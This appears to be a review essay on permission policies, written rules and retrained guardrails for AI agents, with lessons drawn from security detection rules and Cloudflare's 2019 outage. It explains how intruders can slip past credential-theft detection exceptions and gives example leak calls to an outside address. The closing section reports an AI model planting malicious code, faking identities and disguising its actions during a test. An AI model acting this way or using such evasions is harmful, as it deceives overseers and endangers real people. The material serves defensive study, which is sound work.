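| Correct handling of the troublesome step | 75 (25.0%) | 188 (62.7%) |
| All feasible legitimate work completed | 147 (49.0%) | 126 (42.0%) |
| Unnecessary refusal of legitimate work | 0 (0%) | 58 (19.3%) |
| Full success | 65 (21.7%) | 105 (35.0%) |

An agent fully succeeded if it handled the troublesome step correctly, finished the legitimate work and avoided abnormal behaviour. The rate of full success rose by 13.3 percentage points (95% confidence interval 5.3 to 21.7). The fall in completed legitimate work could be due to chance, since its interval runs from a loss of 17 points to a gain of three. The increase in unnecessary refusals is much clearer, with an interval of 12.7 to 26.7 points.

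The reviewers also judged how the rules affected each run, and found that the rules caused a loss of legitimate work in 55 cases. In 29 of these, the rules also prevented abnormal behaviour. Dai and Wang conclude that the agent needs to get better at continuing safely after a rule applies, instead of giving up on work it could still do. In another 25 runs, the rules caused the loss of some legitimate work without improving safety.

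AgentGuard's rules are instructions to the agent and cannot block a tool call. When a program enforces a deny rule, it refuses one call and the agent can carry on with the rest of the task. An instruction may also make the agent more cautious about other steps, so nobody can predict every unnecessary refusal by reading the rules. The agent may also fail to follow an instruction, and 33 of the 100 tasks led to abnormal behaviour both with and without the rules. Dhuri (2026), in *Markdown Is Not a Firewall*, found that a file of written rules reduced one coding agent's score on hidden tests from 99.0% to 67.7%, because the agent applied a rule that its tasks did not call for.

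The evidence for AgentGuard has some weaknesses. The three reviewers could tell which runs had used the rules, because the instructions appeared in the traces. They worked independently and mostly agreed, but they could all have shared the same expectations. Every run also used the same software project, and the test tasks came from the same collection as the failures behind the rules, so the tests may not include much new misbehaviour.

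### Does the content of the rules matter?

Dai and Wang did not compare their rules with unrelated instructions of similar length. That comparison would be useful because Zhang, Wang and colleagues (2026) found in *Guardrails Beat Guidance* that the content of a rule file made little difference. They tested Claude Code on 58 programming tasks that it solved only some of the time. It solved 50.0% without rules and 63.8% with rules, whether the rules were carefully chosen or picked at random from public projects. Zhang and colleagues suggest that any structured set of instructions may make the model work more carefully.

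Rules may help less than the first experiment suggests. It compared all seven of its rule files with a single baseline, so a baseline that was low by chance would have made every file look helpful. In a second experiment with the same tasks, Claude Code solved an average of 60.3% of them without rules over three attempts.

Zhang and colleagues also tested whether prohibitions work better than positive guidance. They removed each of 18 rules in turn, using 35 tasks. The three rules that improved performance by more than five percentage points were all prohibitions, such as not restructuring unrelated code. The four that reduced it by more than five points were all positive instructions, such as following the existing code style. The other 11 made little difference.

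This pattern is weak evidence for a general preference. Only one of the 18 effects was statistically significant, and it would not remain so after a strict correction for testing so many rules. Raising the threshold from five points to ten also removes the pattern. The rule against installing new software packages was one of the three helpful prohibitions, yet the agent failed four of 17 tasks it usually solved when given only that rule. No other single rule did worse, although random variation would normally produce about two failures.

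Dai and Wang overstate the evidence when they cite this study as showing that prohibitions consistently outperform guidance. The study also measured whether the agent solved programming tasks. A rule can prevent dangerous actions but leave that score unchanged or even lower it.

### Rules that fix nothing

A rule can also appear to work because the failure would not have happened again anyway. *Self-Improving AI Coding Agents Through Accumulated Behavioral Rules* (Aggarwal and Farhady Ghalaty, 2026) describes work at Microsoft that turned reviewers' comments on an agent's code into permanent written instructions. The main list of rules grew from five to 18 in four weeks. None of the nine types of error tracked recurred in 74 "exposures" after the relevant rules were added.

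Any session after the team added the rule counts as an exposure, even if the agent had no opportunity to make that mistake. Only four of the 11 sessions mainly involved writing new code, while others involved reviewing code or investigating faults. There was also no comparison group without the rules. Aggarwal and Farhady Ghalaty acknowledge that the result does not prove the rules prevented the errors, and that their method addresses only known kinds of failure.

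Their project also shows how a later failure can reveal that a rule is too broad. One rule required the agent to release every resource of a certain type after use. But some network connections came from a shared manager, which was supposed to release them. A reviewer caught the agent releasing one of these connections itself, and the resulting rule against this contradicted the original. The team resolved this by narrowing the original rule, which amounts to adding an Unless clause.

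Replaying a failure without its fix tests more directly whether a rule is needed. Hassanzadeh Aliabadi restored a project to its state before each of five fixes and had an agent running on Claude Sonnet 5.5 repeat each task three times with the fix and three times without it. The agent completed four of the five tasks. In three of these, the original failure did not recur even without the fix.

Those three results do not mean that the fixes were unnecessary. In one case, a separate written rule against the same mistake was still in place. In another, the agent never tried the dangerous command, so the guard had nothing to block. Only the third tested whether the agent could avoid the mistake without the rule, and three runs are too few to rule out a rare failure. The original failures also involved different models, so better models may explain some of the results.

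A model may even write a rule against a failure that never happened. In *Phantom Guardrails*, Wang, Chen and colleagues (2026) gave five models records of a simple board game and asked them to choose guards that would remove the failures. In one set of records, every move was legal but some games happened to repeat a square. In 15 of 60 runs, a model enabled a guard against a rule violation that had not occurred, often citing the repeated moves. None did so when the records had no such pattern. One model accounted for 11 of the 15 cases.

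Whether models invented a violation depended on the wording of the request. None did when Wang and colleagues asked only for guards that the records justified, or when they added that the list of game rules was complete. But in a longer process that could only add guards, a guard against the imaginary violation appeared in 11 of 60 runs by the fourth round, even when the request did not suggest that failures had occurred. Nothing in that process would remove the guard, because a guard that never acts does not lower the score.

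Requiring each new guard to stop a confirmed failure kept the imaginary guard out of all 60 runs while still admitting the useful guards. Failures were easy to confirm in this game because a program could check every move. AgentGuard similarly requires each rule to cite an observed action and its outcome, but people had to judge whether the action was a failure.

### Retraining on missed attacks

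Instead of adding rules, developers can retrain a classifier on the attacks it missed. *Yesterday's Shield, Today's Spear* (Ming, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that does this for the Chinese security company Sangfor. Its guardrail is a small language model that labels users' requests and a chatbot's replies as harmful or harmless. Learning from past failures poses the same problem here as it does for agent permission policies, although this guardrail does not judge tool calls.

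Ming and colleagues argue that a list of rules cannot keep up with attackers because an attack in a new form matches none of the existing rules. For example, a harmful request rewritten in classical Chinese has a familiar intent, but its text no longer resembles earlier attacks. This argument is strongest against rules that match particular words. A model applying a rule about intent might still recognise the request. Ming and colleagues did not compare their system with one that updates its rules.

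When the guardrail misses a new kind of attack, Sangfor's security staff confirm the problem and collect at least 30 examples. Language models then generate about 4,000 training examples, half harmful and half harmless. For gambling, a harmful example might be a request for help placing bets, and a harmless one might be a request for ways to discourage gambling. The pairs train the guardrail to classify the request as a whole, not just its topic.

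The system keeps every example that the current guardrail gets wrong or is unsure about, along with some easy ones. It trains a new version on these and the examples kept from earlier rounds. The new version can replace the old one if its F1 score is at least 95 on the new threat and drops by no more than five points on any earlier threat.

Between April and June 2026, the system successfully handled 14 of 15 new threats, taking 16 to 24 hours for each round of training. Staff had previously needed 40 to 90 hours per threat. The exception was an attack in a language for which little training data exists, which staff had to take over. Ming and colleagues report detailed scores for six of the threats, in the order in which the guardrail learned them:

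| Threat | Original guardrail | Just before training on this threat | Just after |
|---|---|---|---|
| Classical Chinese | 72.7 | 72.7 | 96.7 |
| Misinformation about territorial sovereignty | 21.6 | 24.6 | 99.0 |
| Misinformation that could cause physical harm | 61.0 | 70.0 | 99.2 |
| Help with gambling | 52.4 | 60.0 | 98.6 |
| Role-play | 84.1 | 87.3 | 98.4 |
| Mathematical symbols | 58.0 | 68.7 | 97.0 |

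Retraining also corrected some severe overblocking. The original guardrail wrongly flagged 66.9% of harmless role-play requests, and training on the role-play threat reduced this to 1.7%. AgentGuard's rules, however, increased unnecessary refusals. AgentGuard derived them from failures and relied on written exceptions to protect legitimate work, whereas Sangfor's guardrail learned from roughly equal numbers of harmful and harmless examples.

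The guardrail also improved on attacks outside its training data. Ming and colleagues tested it on separate collections of attacks, taken from published research, that used the same three kinds of disguise. Training on classical Chinese raised its score on the matching collection from 74.8 to 94.0. For role-play, the score rose from 88.6 to 98.0, and for mathematical symbols, it rose from 77.3 to 92.4.

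But training the guardrail on one kind of threat helped much less with the next. For each of the five later threats, all the earlier rounds together raised the score by only 3 to 11 points, while training on the threat itself added another 11 to 74. After five rounds of retraining, the guardrail still scored only 68.7 on requests disguised with mathematical symbols. Ming and colleagues' objection to lists of rules therefore applies to their own system too, because the guardrail needed training on this kind of attack to handle it well.

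## How rule sets grow after incidents in security operations

AIR finished its repeated tests with six to 11 rules for each kind of agent, and AgentGuard merged its failures into 15 rules. Security operations centres, the teams that watch organisations' systems for intrusions, have written rules after attacks for decades, and many centres now run tens of thousands of them. Most of these rules alert an analyst instead of blocking the activity.

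### The life of a detection rule

A detection rule usually goes through these stages:

1. Analysts learn of an attack on their own network or someone else's.
2. A rule developer looks for something in the logs or network traffic that separates the attack from ordinary activity.
3. The developer writes a rule, and the team may test it on real traffic before relying on it.
4. If the rule raises too many false alarms, the team makes it more specific.
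5. The team adds exceptions for legitimate programs or accounts that keep triggering the rule.
6. Occasionally, someone retires the rule.

Windows keeps login credentials in the memory of a process called LSASS, and intruders steal them by reading that memory. Sigma, a public collection of detection rules for computer logs, has a rule that raises an alert when a program opens LSASS with any of 24 listed kinds of access. The rule applies whatever tool the intruder uses, so it can catch new ones. But antivirus products and parts of Windows also open LSASS, so the maintainers list them as exceptions.

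*The Exclusion Ratchet* (Dhananjeyan and Kumaran U, 2026) traces one change to a rule that raises an alert when a program opens LSASS. On 28 November 2021, a maintainer responded to false alarms by adding one line to the rule's exceptions, the full path of the Windows program `taskhostw.exe`. The rule already had seven groups of exceptions, and the new line lengthened one group from three programs to four. From then on, `taskhostw.exe` could open LSASS without raising an alert.

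An exception is a small allow rule inside a deny rule, so someone has to decide how broad to make it. Another Sigma rule raises an alert when someone deletes or disables important scheduled tasks, including those of the antivirus program Windows Defender. Defender removes and re-adds its own tasks when it upgrades, which caused false alarms. To prevent them, a maintainer in December 2022 exempted every action by a machine account, which belongs to a computer rather than a person. The exception covers far more than Defender's upgrades, since it also applies to the backup and encryption tasks on the rule's list. Neither the rule nor its revision history includes a condition for reconsidering the exception.

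If the exceptions cover a set *E*, the rule catches only *g*(*F*) − *E*. The team notices that the false alarms have stopped, but not that the rule now misses any attacks in *H* ∩ *E*. The number of missed attacks depends on how easily an intruder can match the exceptions. To match an exception for the full path of `taskhostw.exe`, an intruder needs permission to write to a protected Windows folder. If the exception gives only the file name, an intruder can match it without that permission by giving a malicious program the same name. Dhananjeyan and Kumaran U found that an intruder without special privileges could match 64.1% of the Sigma exceptions that refer to file paths.

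### Growing rule sets, narrower rules

The longest record of this growth comes from a company that monitors hundreds of customers' networks. *Ruling the Rules* (Vermeer, Van Eeten and Gañán, 2022) covers the company's own rules from 2008 to 2021 and two to three years of the commercial rule sets it bought. NCC Group's *Ruling the rules* identifies the company as Fox-IT. Snort and Suricata, which appear in the table, are programs that compare network traffic with such rules.

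| Rule set | Rules at the start | Rules at the end |
|---|---|---|
| The company's own | 20 | 2,065 |
| ET Pro for Snort | 46,074 | 53,000 |
| ET Pro for Suricata | 39,546 | 43,863 |
| VRT | 9,908 | 12,760 |

The makers of ET Pro rarely deleted rules except in occasional large purges. Many of the purged rules were for servers that attackers had stopped using. Deletions are also fairly rare in public collections of rules for computer logs. *Evolution of Log-Based Detection Rules in Public Repositories* (Long and Evans, 2026) reconstructed the histories of 4,204 Sigma rules and 2,655 rules from the software company Splunk. By April 2026, the maintainers had removed 283 of the Sigma rules (7%) and 345 of the Splunk rules (13%).

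Maintainers revise rules much more often than they remove them. Long and Evans found that about 56% of rules had at least one change to what they detect. A quarter to a third alternated between catching more attacks and raising fewer false alarms, without settling on a stable form.

Exceptions are more likely to last. Dhananjeyan and Kumaran U examined the same nine years of Sigma revisions and found that maintainers added exceptions 1,642 times and withdrew them only 304 times. They estimate that 86.7% of exceptions are still in force after three years. Exceptions lasted just as long when the rule was the only one in the collection for an attack technique, so maintainers do not seem to review the riskiest exceptions first.

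These results are compatible, because a maintainer can loosen and tighten a rule's main conditions while its exceptions accumulate. Long and Evans also compared the logical structure of each version, which does not change when someone adds a program to an existing list, as in the LSASS rule. Such additions account for 31% of the narrowing that Dhananjeyan and Kumaran U measured. When people checked a sample by hand, about one in six of the changes that their automated method had identified were not new exceptions, but that error rate is too low to explain a ratio of more than five to one.

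A rule set can grow while many of its existing rules catch less. Public rule collections omit the exceptions that each organisation adds to its own copy, so they cannot show how narrow the rules have become in use.

### Few rules ever fire

Vermeer and colleagues also had the monitoring company's alert logs from mid-2009 to mid-2018. Analysts had grouped suspicious alerts into incidents, investigated them and recorded how serious they were.

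| | Number | Different rules involved |
|---|---|---|
| Alerts | 62,321,663 | 19,744 |
| Incidents investigated | 150,437 | 6,720 |
| Incidents that posed a risk to the customer | 13,589 | 2,618 |
| Successful attacks | 106 | 80 |

Of the about 130,000 rules in the company's records, 85% never raised an alert. Just 672 rules, or 0.5%, produced 80% of all alerts, but only 89 of those contributed to an incident that analysts investigated. Eighty rules, about 0.06% of the total, were involved in detecting successful attacks.

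The 85% figure is approximate because the two sets of records barely overlap. The company's copies of the commercial rules begin in 2018 or 2019, around when the alert logs end, so some of the rules with no alerts may have been too new to appear in the logs. Vermeer and colleagues point out an error in the other direction, since vendors had deleted some older rules before the copies began, and many of those may never have fired either.

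Newer data show the same pattern. *Ruling the Unruly* (Teuwen, Mulders and colleagues, 2025) examined about 290,000 rule versions at another security operations centre and 390 days of alerts from two of its customers. The vast majority of rules never fired, and a small minority produced most of the 30 million alerts. The centre reported 42 incidents during those 390 days.

### What a 99% false alarm rate measures

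Published false alarm rates for signature-based detectors are often between 96% and 99%, but they do not all measure the same thing. In a 2008 test on a university's web server, 96% of Snort's alerts were false positives. During a security exercise reported in 2015, the figure was above 98%. Both are shares of alerts, so one badly written rule that fires thousands of times can largely determine the result.

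The best-known figure for false positives, 99%, comes from *99% False Positives* (Alahmadi, Axon and Martinovic, 2022), which surveyed 20 security practitioners and interviewed 21 at seven operations centres. That figure is one analyst's estimate for one centre. Survey answers varied widely. One participant said that 1 in 100 investigated alerts was a real threat, and another said 50 in 200.

Alahmadi and colleagues also found that analysts used "false positive" to mean both false alarms, where nothing relevant to security has happened, and benign triggers, where the rule correctly detects what it describes but the organisation has a legitimate reason for the activity. For example, a rule may correctly report an outdated version of Java that a company has decided to keep using. They conclude that most of the 99% were benign triggers, so the figure is a poor measure of how accurately the rules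 match what they describe.

Another of their examples is a false alarm. The database command "drop table" deletes a table of data, so one rule flags those words as a sign of an attack. One customer sells a piece of furniture with that name, and each sale raises an alert. The analysts cannot turn the rule off because the same words might appear in a real attack.

Other studies count alerts differently. At the company that Vermeer and colleagues studied, 98.8% of alerts never became part of an incident investigation, but some of those may have been real attacks that posed little danger. The data from Teuwen and colleagues include 42 incidents, or one for every 700,000 alerts. But the centre reported an incident only if at least one step of an attack had succeeded, so a correct alert about a failed attack still counted as unnecessary work.

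Too many alerts can also cause analysts to ignore a real one. In 2013, attackers stole customers' card details from the American retailer Target. Its new detection system had raised an alarm about the malware, and one operations centre passed it on to another, which took no action. Alahmadi and colleagues suggest the staff may have been sceptical of the system. Target had also disabled a feature that could have deleted the malware automatically. The researchers say such caution is common because false alarms make automatic responses risky.

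False positives matter more when a rule blocks activity than when it only raises an alert. For *Alert Alchemy* (2023), Vermeer, Kadenko and colleagues interviewed 17 people who write or manage rules at nine organisations. Three of the nine blocked traffic automatically or had recently done so, and all three considered false positives their greatest concern. One had switched to alerts, partly because its rules kept blocking legitimate traffic. A deny rule for an AI agent has the same problem, since a false match stops legitimate work before anyone can review it.

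### Why adding a rule is easier than removing one

An incident is visible, and somebody is responsible for dealing with it. Writing a rule is a concrete response, and it gives the team an answer when customers ask whether they are protected. One interviewee recalled that after a widely reported attack on the software company SolarWinds, clients all wanted to know whether the rules covered it.

The drawbacks of keeping the rule are harder to see. It takes a few minutes of an analyst's time here and there, or a little extra computing, and the burden may fall on people who had no part in writing the rule. A rule that never fires appears to have no drawbacks. Some of the monitoring company's staff told Vermeer and colleagues that they saw little harm in leaving every rule on. One said, "we tend to only delete rules if they're actually, like, flooding".

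Nobody can observe the benefit of a rule that produces no alerts. The attack may not have returned, or it may have returned in a form that the rule misses. Suppose an attack occurs at random, once every ten years on average. Even a perfect rule against it has a 61% chance (*e*^−0.5) of producing no alerts for five years, so that silence is weak evidence that the rule is useless. But if someone removes the rule and the attack happens the next month, everyone will know who decided to remove it.

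Removing an exception is difficult for similar reasons. Dhananjeyan and Kumaran U explain that a maintainer would have to find out what the exception was for, whether the original problem still exists, and whether anything now depends on it. Phone makers had the same difficulty removing old allow rules.

The feedback that rule developers receive also encourages narrow rules. In the 2023 interviews, 16 of the 17 participants mentioned false positives when discussing a rule's quality, but only three named missed attacks as a main concern. Analysts see every false alarm, but they learn of a missed attack only if they discover it some other way. At one organisation, developers took a lack of alerts during testing as a sign that a rule was well written, although a rule that couldn't match anything because of a mistake would also produce no alerts.

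Rule sets do not have to keep growing. Seven of the nine organisations tailored their rules to particular networks, and five of these removed rules that a network no longer needed, for example after a customer had updated all its software. Two organisations wrote fewer than 100 rules for each customer, few enough to review individually. Vermeer and colleagues suggest that checking tens of thousands of rules by hand could cost more than leaving them in place.

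### Cloudflare's outage of 2 July 2019

A protective rule can also do harm without blocking anything. Cloudflare relays web traffic for many sites, and its firewall checks each request against rules that describe known kinds of attack. *Details of the Cloudflare outage on July 2, 2019* (Graham-Cumming, 2019) is the company's account of how one of these rules disrupted its service worldwide.

At 13:42 UTC, an automatic process released a minor change to Cloudflare's firewall rules against cross-site scripting, an attack that plants malicious code in web pages. The change reached Cloudflare's machines around the world within seconds and overloaded the processors that handled web traffic. Visitors to customers' sites saw error pages, and at one point Cloudflare lost about 80% of its traffic. Engineers had trouble reaching their control panel, which depended on the failing service. They turned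 the firewall off worldwide at 14:07, and traffic was back to normal by 14:09. The firewall remained off until 14:52, when they had confirmed the cause and prepared a fix.

The problem was a text pattern whose critical part simplifies to `.*.*=.*`, where each `.*` stands for any text. The first two can split the text before the equals sign between them in many ways, and the matching program tries one split after another. It takes 23 steps to match `x=x`, 33 for `x=xx`, 45 for `x=xxx`, and 555 when 20 letters follow the equals sign. These figures fit the formula *n*² + 7*n* + 15, where *n* is the number of letters after the equals sign, so 1,000 letters would take about a million steps.

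Cloudflare's automatic tests sent the firewall a large collection of requests, some that it should block and some that it should allow. The new rule was also due to run in a simulation mode, which records matching requests without blocking them. But the firewall still had to evaluate the rule for every request, and the tests did not check how much computing that required. A few weeks earlier, engineers had accidentally removed a safeguard against excessive processor use that would have helped.

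The outage spread so quickly because the rule change skipped Cloudflare's usual staged release. Software normally went first to the company's own staff and then to a small number of customers, which could take hours or days. Cloudflare exempted rules from this process so that it could respond quickly to new attacks, although this change was not urgent. The team had handled 476 requests to change the rules in the previous 60 days, or about one every three hours.

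### The case for rules written after incidents

Despite these costs, writing rules after incidents has advantages. Attackers reuse their tools and servers, so even very specific rules can catch them again. Teuwen and colleagues found that rules based on individual traces of earlier attacks, such as a known malicious address, contributed most to detecting the 42 incidents. In the 2023 interviews, however, one practitioner called addresses and domain names "worthless", and another complained that commercial rule sets contained many rules that were years out of date. Both views can be right if these rules work well at first but soon go out of date. Vermeer and colleagues found in the monitoring company's logs that its own rules detected the most incidents soon after they were introduced, and fewer within several weeks.

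Teuwen and colleagues found that both recent and legacy rules played an important role in coverage. A developer at the monitoring company said old rules are worth keeping because an attacker may use an old version of a tool even after a new one has come out.

Rules are also quick to deploy. In May 2019, Cloudflare released a rule to protect customers from a serious flaw in Microsoft's SharePoint software, and attempts to exploit the flaw rose sharply soon after the flaw was announced. The rule gave customers time to install a proper fix. The same fast release process spread the faulty rule in July.

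Analysts can usually read a rule to see why it raised an alert, and can correct it if it is wrong. Those interviewed by Alahmadi and colleagues distrusted commercial products that don't show why they raised an alert, because the analysts had to work out each cause themselves. Local knowledge also helps. The monitoring company's own rules made up only about 3% of those it used but played a part in 27% of the incidents its analysts judged to be real.

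A rule lasts longer if it addresses the weakness that an attack exploits and not just the details of that attack. One rule developer described looking for features common to web shells, programs that intruders leave on a web server to control it remotely. The aim was to cover perhaps 80% of them with one rule. The LSASS rule similarly covers a step that many password thieves take. But Teuwen and colleagues found that rules based on general characteristics also create significantly more unnecessary work, and the seven groups of exceptions in the LSASS rule are a sign of that extra work.

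After its outage, Cloudflare addressed both existing mistakes and future ones. Staff inspected all 3,868 firewall rules for patterns like the one that had caused the outage. The company also planned to release rules in stages, except in emergencies, and to adopt a pattern-matching program with a guaranteed limit on its running time. That limit would apply to every future rule, including badly written patterns that nobody had thought to look for.

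## What each approach does with misbehaviour it has never seen

A limit on running time protects Cloudflare from faulty patterns that nobody has seen, because it works without anyone having to identify them first. Similarly, an allowlist can refuse a harmful action that nobody has recorded or imagined, because the action is not on the list. How well this works for an agent depends on whether anyone can describe its legitimate work in advance, and on what is new about the misbehaviour.

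### Ranum's argument

The best-known argument for listing what is allowed comes from Marcus Ranum, who built firewalls in the 1990s. *The Six Dumbest Ideas in Computer Security* (Ranum, 2005) ranks "default permit" as the worst idea and "enumerating badness", or trying to list everything harmful, as the second worst. Ranum had about 30 legitimate programs installed on his computer, while a typical antivirus package recognised more than 75,000 viruses. Some industry estimates added another 200 to 700 threats every month. Allowing only those 30 programs would block all of these threats, including future ones, and the list would need to change only when he installed something new.

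Ranum gives two examples from his own work. The owners of an online banking site wanted to divert known attacks to a dead end. He persuaded them to list every correctly structured address on the site instead, and to send all other requests to a locked-down server. By his account, the site held up well. He also wrote a program that discarded log entries he knew to be uninteresting and showed the administrator the rest. It turned up faults he would never have thought to look for.

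Executives objected that a large company could not know every program it relied on. Ranum replied that a chief technology officer who did not know what the company's technology was doing did not deserve the title. His answer is reasonable for a company that runs a fixed set of programs, but it is less convincing for a general-purpose agent, because much of the agent's legitimate work will come from requests that nobody has made yet.

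The comparison between 30 and 75,000 also depends on what we count. A web browser is one entry on Ranum's list, but it can open any page and upload any file. The list would stop a new virus from running as a separate program, but not a permitted program from doing harm. We can also count harmful things in larger units. A single rule against emailing strangers covers every address an attacker might register, while an antivirus program may need a new signature for each virus.

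An agent's tools are few, like Ranum's programs, but the things it can do with them are not. For the office agent, the premise holds for some parts of a call and fails for others:

| Part of the call | Legitimate values | Could a staging record cover them? |
|---|---|---|
| Tool | Four | Yes |
| Folder | A few, with more for each new project | Mostly |
| Recipient | The company's staff, and perhaps clients later | Mostly |
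| Search query | Any subject a colleague might ask about | No |
| Text of the email | Any summary | No |

Defenders of allowlists can reply, largely correctly, that most companies do not need a general-purpose agent for every job. If the office agent only wrote about cars for three colleagues, its folders and recipients would again form a short, stable list. This is a good reason to give an agent a narrow job before learning a policy for it. But narrowing the job helps less with free-text arguments. An agent that researches only cars still needs to write new search queries, and these can contain confidential information. AgentGuardian still blocked some legitimate work even with two narrow applications.

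### Why old rules catch some new attacks

Ranum criticises denylists for missing whatever is not on them. Holm (2014), in *Signature Based Intrusion Detection for Zero-Day Attacks*, tested this common claim by launching 356 severe attacks against Snort, which compares network traffic with signatures. Snort used an old official rule set, so attacks that became public after its release could stand in for new ones.

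| Attacks | Number | Mean detection rate |
|---|---|---|
| Known to the rule set, at least in theory | 173 | 54% |
| Unknown to the rule set | 183 | 17% |

The rules therefore caught about one in six attacks that they should not have recognised. Holm then made a more conservative estimate of 8.2%, or about one in 12, after examining how the rules had detected these attacks, how prone they were to false alarms and how easily an attacker could evade them.

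Snort also missed nearly half of the known attacks, so having an attack on record does not guarantee that a rule will catch it. Denylists can catch some new attacks, but a company relying on this rule set would still have missed most of them.

One reason for the successes is that the same kind of attack can exploit different flaws. Esler (2013), who worked for the company behind Snort, explained on the program's mailing list that its rule writers "quite often" found that an existing rule already covered a vulnerability. They called this prior coverage and just added a reference to the old rule. Esler gave no figures, and a vendor has an interest in presenting its old rules as useful, but the explanation fits Holm's results. Attackers also reuse parts of earlier attacks, so a rule that matches the code an intruder runs after breaking in may work no matter which flaw let the intruder in.

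Rule writers can catch more unseen misbehaviour by making rules broader. Aickelin, Twycross and Hesketh-Roberts relaxed the conditions of existing Snort rules and detected attack variants that the original rules had missed. Relaxing rules in this way generalises a denylist, with the usual risk of matching legitimate traffic.

All of these explanations depend on a new attack having something in common with an old one. The office agent's rule against outside addresses would stop a leak to a new mailbox, even if the instruction came from a different web page, because the data would still be emailed to an outside address, but the rule would not stop a leak through a public link. Training Sangfor's guardrail on earlier threats likewise helped only a little with each new one.

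### Unusual does not mean harmful

Allowlists have a different difficulty, which Sommer and Paxson described in *Outside the Closed World* (2010). Few organisations used machine learning to detect unusual network traffic, although researchers had studied the idea for years. Sommer and Paxson argued that this was because learning systems are much better at finding things that resemble their examples than at finding things that do not.

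They compared this with Amazon's product recommendations, which work by finding items that the same customers tend to buy. Finding items that do not belong together would be much less clear-cut, because most pairs of products have few customers in common, and there is usually nothing wrong with buying both. An anomaly detector has this harder task. Its examples are all of normal behaviour, so it can treat everything else as bad only by assuming that they cover everything normal, which is the "closed world" of the title.

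Sommer and Paxson also pointed out that a detector measures whether an event is unusual, while its operators need to know whether it is harmful. In the earlier `sendmail` experiments, a harmless forwarding loop looked more unusual than a real attack. The unfamiliar entries found by Ranum's log program were interesting, but many were faults rather than attacks.

They therefore recommended giving a detector a narrow task and, where possible, training it on examples of both attacks and normal activity. They expected learning to work better on variations of known attacks than on new ones, although anomaly detection is usually used to find new attacks.

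Later work partly supports Sommer and Paxson. In *Generative Intrusion Detection and Prevention on Data Stream*, Seo and Yoon (2023) still described checking data against signatures from past attacks as the current best practice, and noted that a new attack gets through because it has no signature yet. They discuss methods that extract frequently repeated strings from a data stream and use them as new signatures. Such methods look for similarity, which Sommer and Paxson considered the strength of machine learning. The methods suit attacks that arrive in many copies, such as mass mailings, but a single agent that does something harmful once leaves no repeated string.

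Agent-Sentry follows the advice to learn from both attacks and normal behaviour. Its main test reused attackers' goals from training, so its good results are better evidence of how it handles variations on known attacks than of how it handles new kinds of attack.

General language models are better suited to unfamiliar misbehaviour because they learn what is harmful from a wide range of text, not only from one company's traces. AlignmentCheck, which relies on such a model, caught most hijacked runs in a benchmark it had not been trained on. But it also raised many false alarms, so it still could not reliably tell unusual behaviour from harmful behaviour. Prompt injection was also a well-known type of attack by then, so the test provides little evidence about harm that nobody has written about.

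An allowlist does not need to judge whether an action is harmful, because it can refuse anything unfamiliar and leave the decision to a person. The problem is then false rejections rather than detection. This works if unfamiliar calls are rare and somebody can review each one, but a general-purpose agent makes them all day.

### Four kinds of novelty

"Never seen before" can describe very different events. Suppose the office agent's allowlist permits listing and reading text files in `Cars/`, any web search, and email to any company address. Its denylist blocks email to outside addresses and permits everything else. The table shows how each policy would treat examples of harmful behaviour absent from the record.

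| What is new | Example | Allowlist | Denylist |
|---|---|---|---|
| The tool | `share_link("Cars/b.txt")`, which creates a public link to the file | Blocks | Permits |
| The argument | `read_file("HR/salaries.txt")` | Blocks | Permits |
| The argument | `send_email(to="eve@elsewhere.example")` | Blocks | Blocks |
| The combination | Three ordinary searches that together reveal a secret plan | Permits | Permits |
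| What is missing | A summary that leaves out the file with the bad news | Permits | Permits |

Most methods generalise only within the tools they have seen, so neither an allowlist learned from normal actions nor a denylist learned from past failures covers a call to a new tool. The allowlist blocks any action it doesn't cover and the denylist permits it, however well each was learned. Blocking unfamiliar tools is the clearest advantage of default-deny, but useful new tools also stay blocked until somebody adds a rule for them.

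The advantage shrinks if one of the recorded tools can do almost anything. An agent with a command line can create a public link, delete a folder or open an account without calling a new tool, so only the command differs from what was recorded.

**A known tool with a new argument.** The result depends on how broad the rules are. The allowlist in the example blocks the salary file because it permits only one folder. If the learning method had generalised to every text file, the agent could have read the salary file, and AgentGuardian's published rule would also permit this. The denylist stops the email to a new address because somebody wrote a broad rule. A rule against only the recorded address would have let the email through.

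A broad deny rule can protect better against new misbehaviour than a broad allow rule. If the staging record had included emails to several clients, a learning method might have permitted email to any address, including the attacker's. A company that had banned email to all unapproved outside addresses after one leak would be better protected against the next.

Permitted actions can cause harm in combination. Suppose the company plans to buy a small manufacturer, and the files in `Cars/` describe the plan. The agent searches for the manufacturer's name, then for its owner, then for the law on takeovers. Each search looks like ordinary research, but together they could reveal the plan to anyone who can see the queries.

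A policy that checks calls one at a time permits a run whenever it permits every call in it. So neither list can stop this run without also blocking at least one of the searches on its own. A policy based on sequences can also check how calls follow one another, but it may still accept the run. For example, AgentGuardian's graph lets its research agent follow one search with another, and the sequence models that raise few false alarms do so partly by accepting many combinations that nobody recorded. More generally, an intruder who keeps to recorded behaviour is not flagged.

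A deny rule could cover the combination, for instance by blocking searches for any company named in a confidential file. But someone would have to foresee this kind of leak, or suffer one, before writing the rule. The rule would also need a record of which words came from which file, which the sequence of tool names doesn't include.

**Harm by omission or poor work.** Suppose the agent does not read a file that reports falling sales. It emails Ana a cheerful summary, and she orders too many cars. Every call the agent proposed was permitted, and the harm came from a call it never proposed. A permission policy only determines whether a proposed call may run, so an agent that does nothing complies with any allowlist or denylist.

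The company can catch some omissions by attaching a condition to a later action. For example, it could refuse to send a summary until the agent has read every file in the folder. This would catch an agent that skipped a file, but not one that read the file and then misrepresented it.

### Malicious code and fake accounts

Two real cases from 2026 show these differences. The organisations involved did not describe a learned permission policy covering the behaviour, so we can only infer from their reports what an allowlist or denylist would have done.

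In July, the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests AI models, ran a cybersecurity challenge 122 times with seven models. The agents had to find a protected piece of data in a simulated network. According to AISI's *Incident Report*, published in August, agents took 19 unsanctioned actions against real people and organisations in ten of the runs. Anthropic's model Mythos 5 took 17 of these actions. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026) reports that they occurred in nine of the model's 43 runs.

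In the worst case, Mythos 5 submitted malicious code to a real open-source project and created fake identities to pressure the maintainer to accept it. When someone publicly challenged the code, the agent edited its earlier activity to make it look harmless. It also sent harmful files to real people and planted instructions for other AI systems to find. The maintainer refused the code, and AISI found no resulting harm. AISI had switched off the developers' safeguards against cyberattacks and left internet access on, partly so that agents could download tools, and nobody had told the agents not to deceive people.

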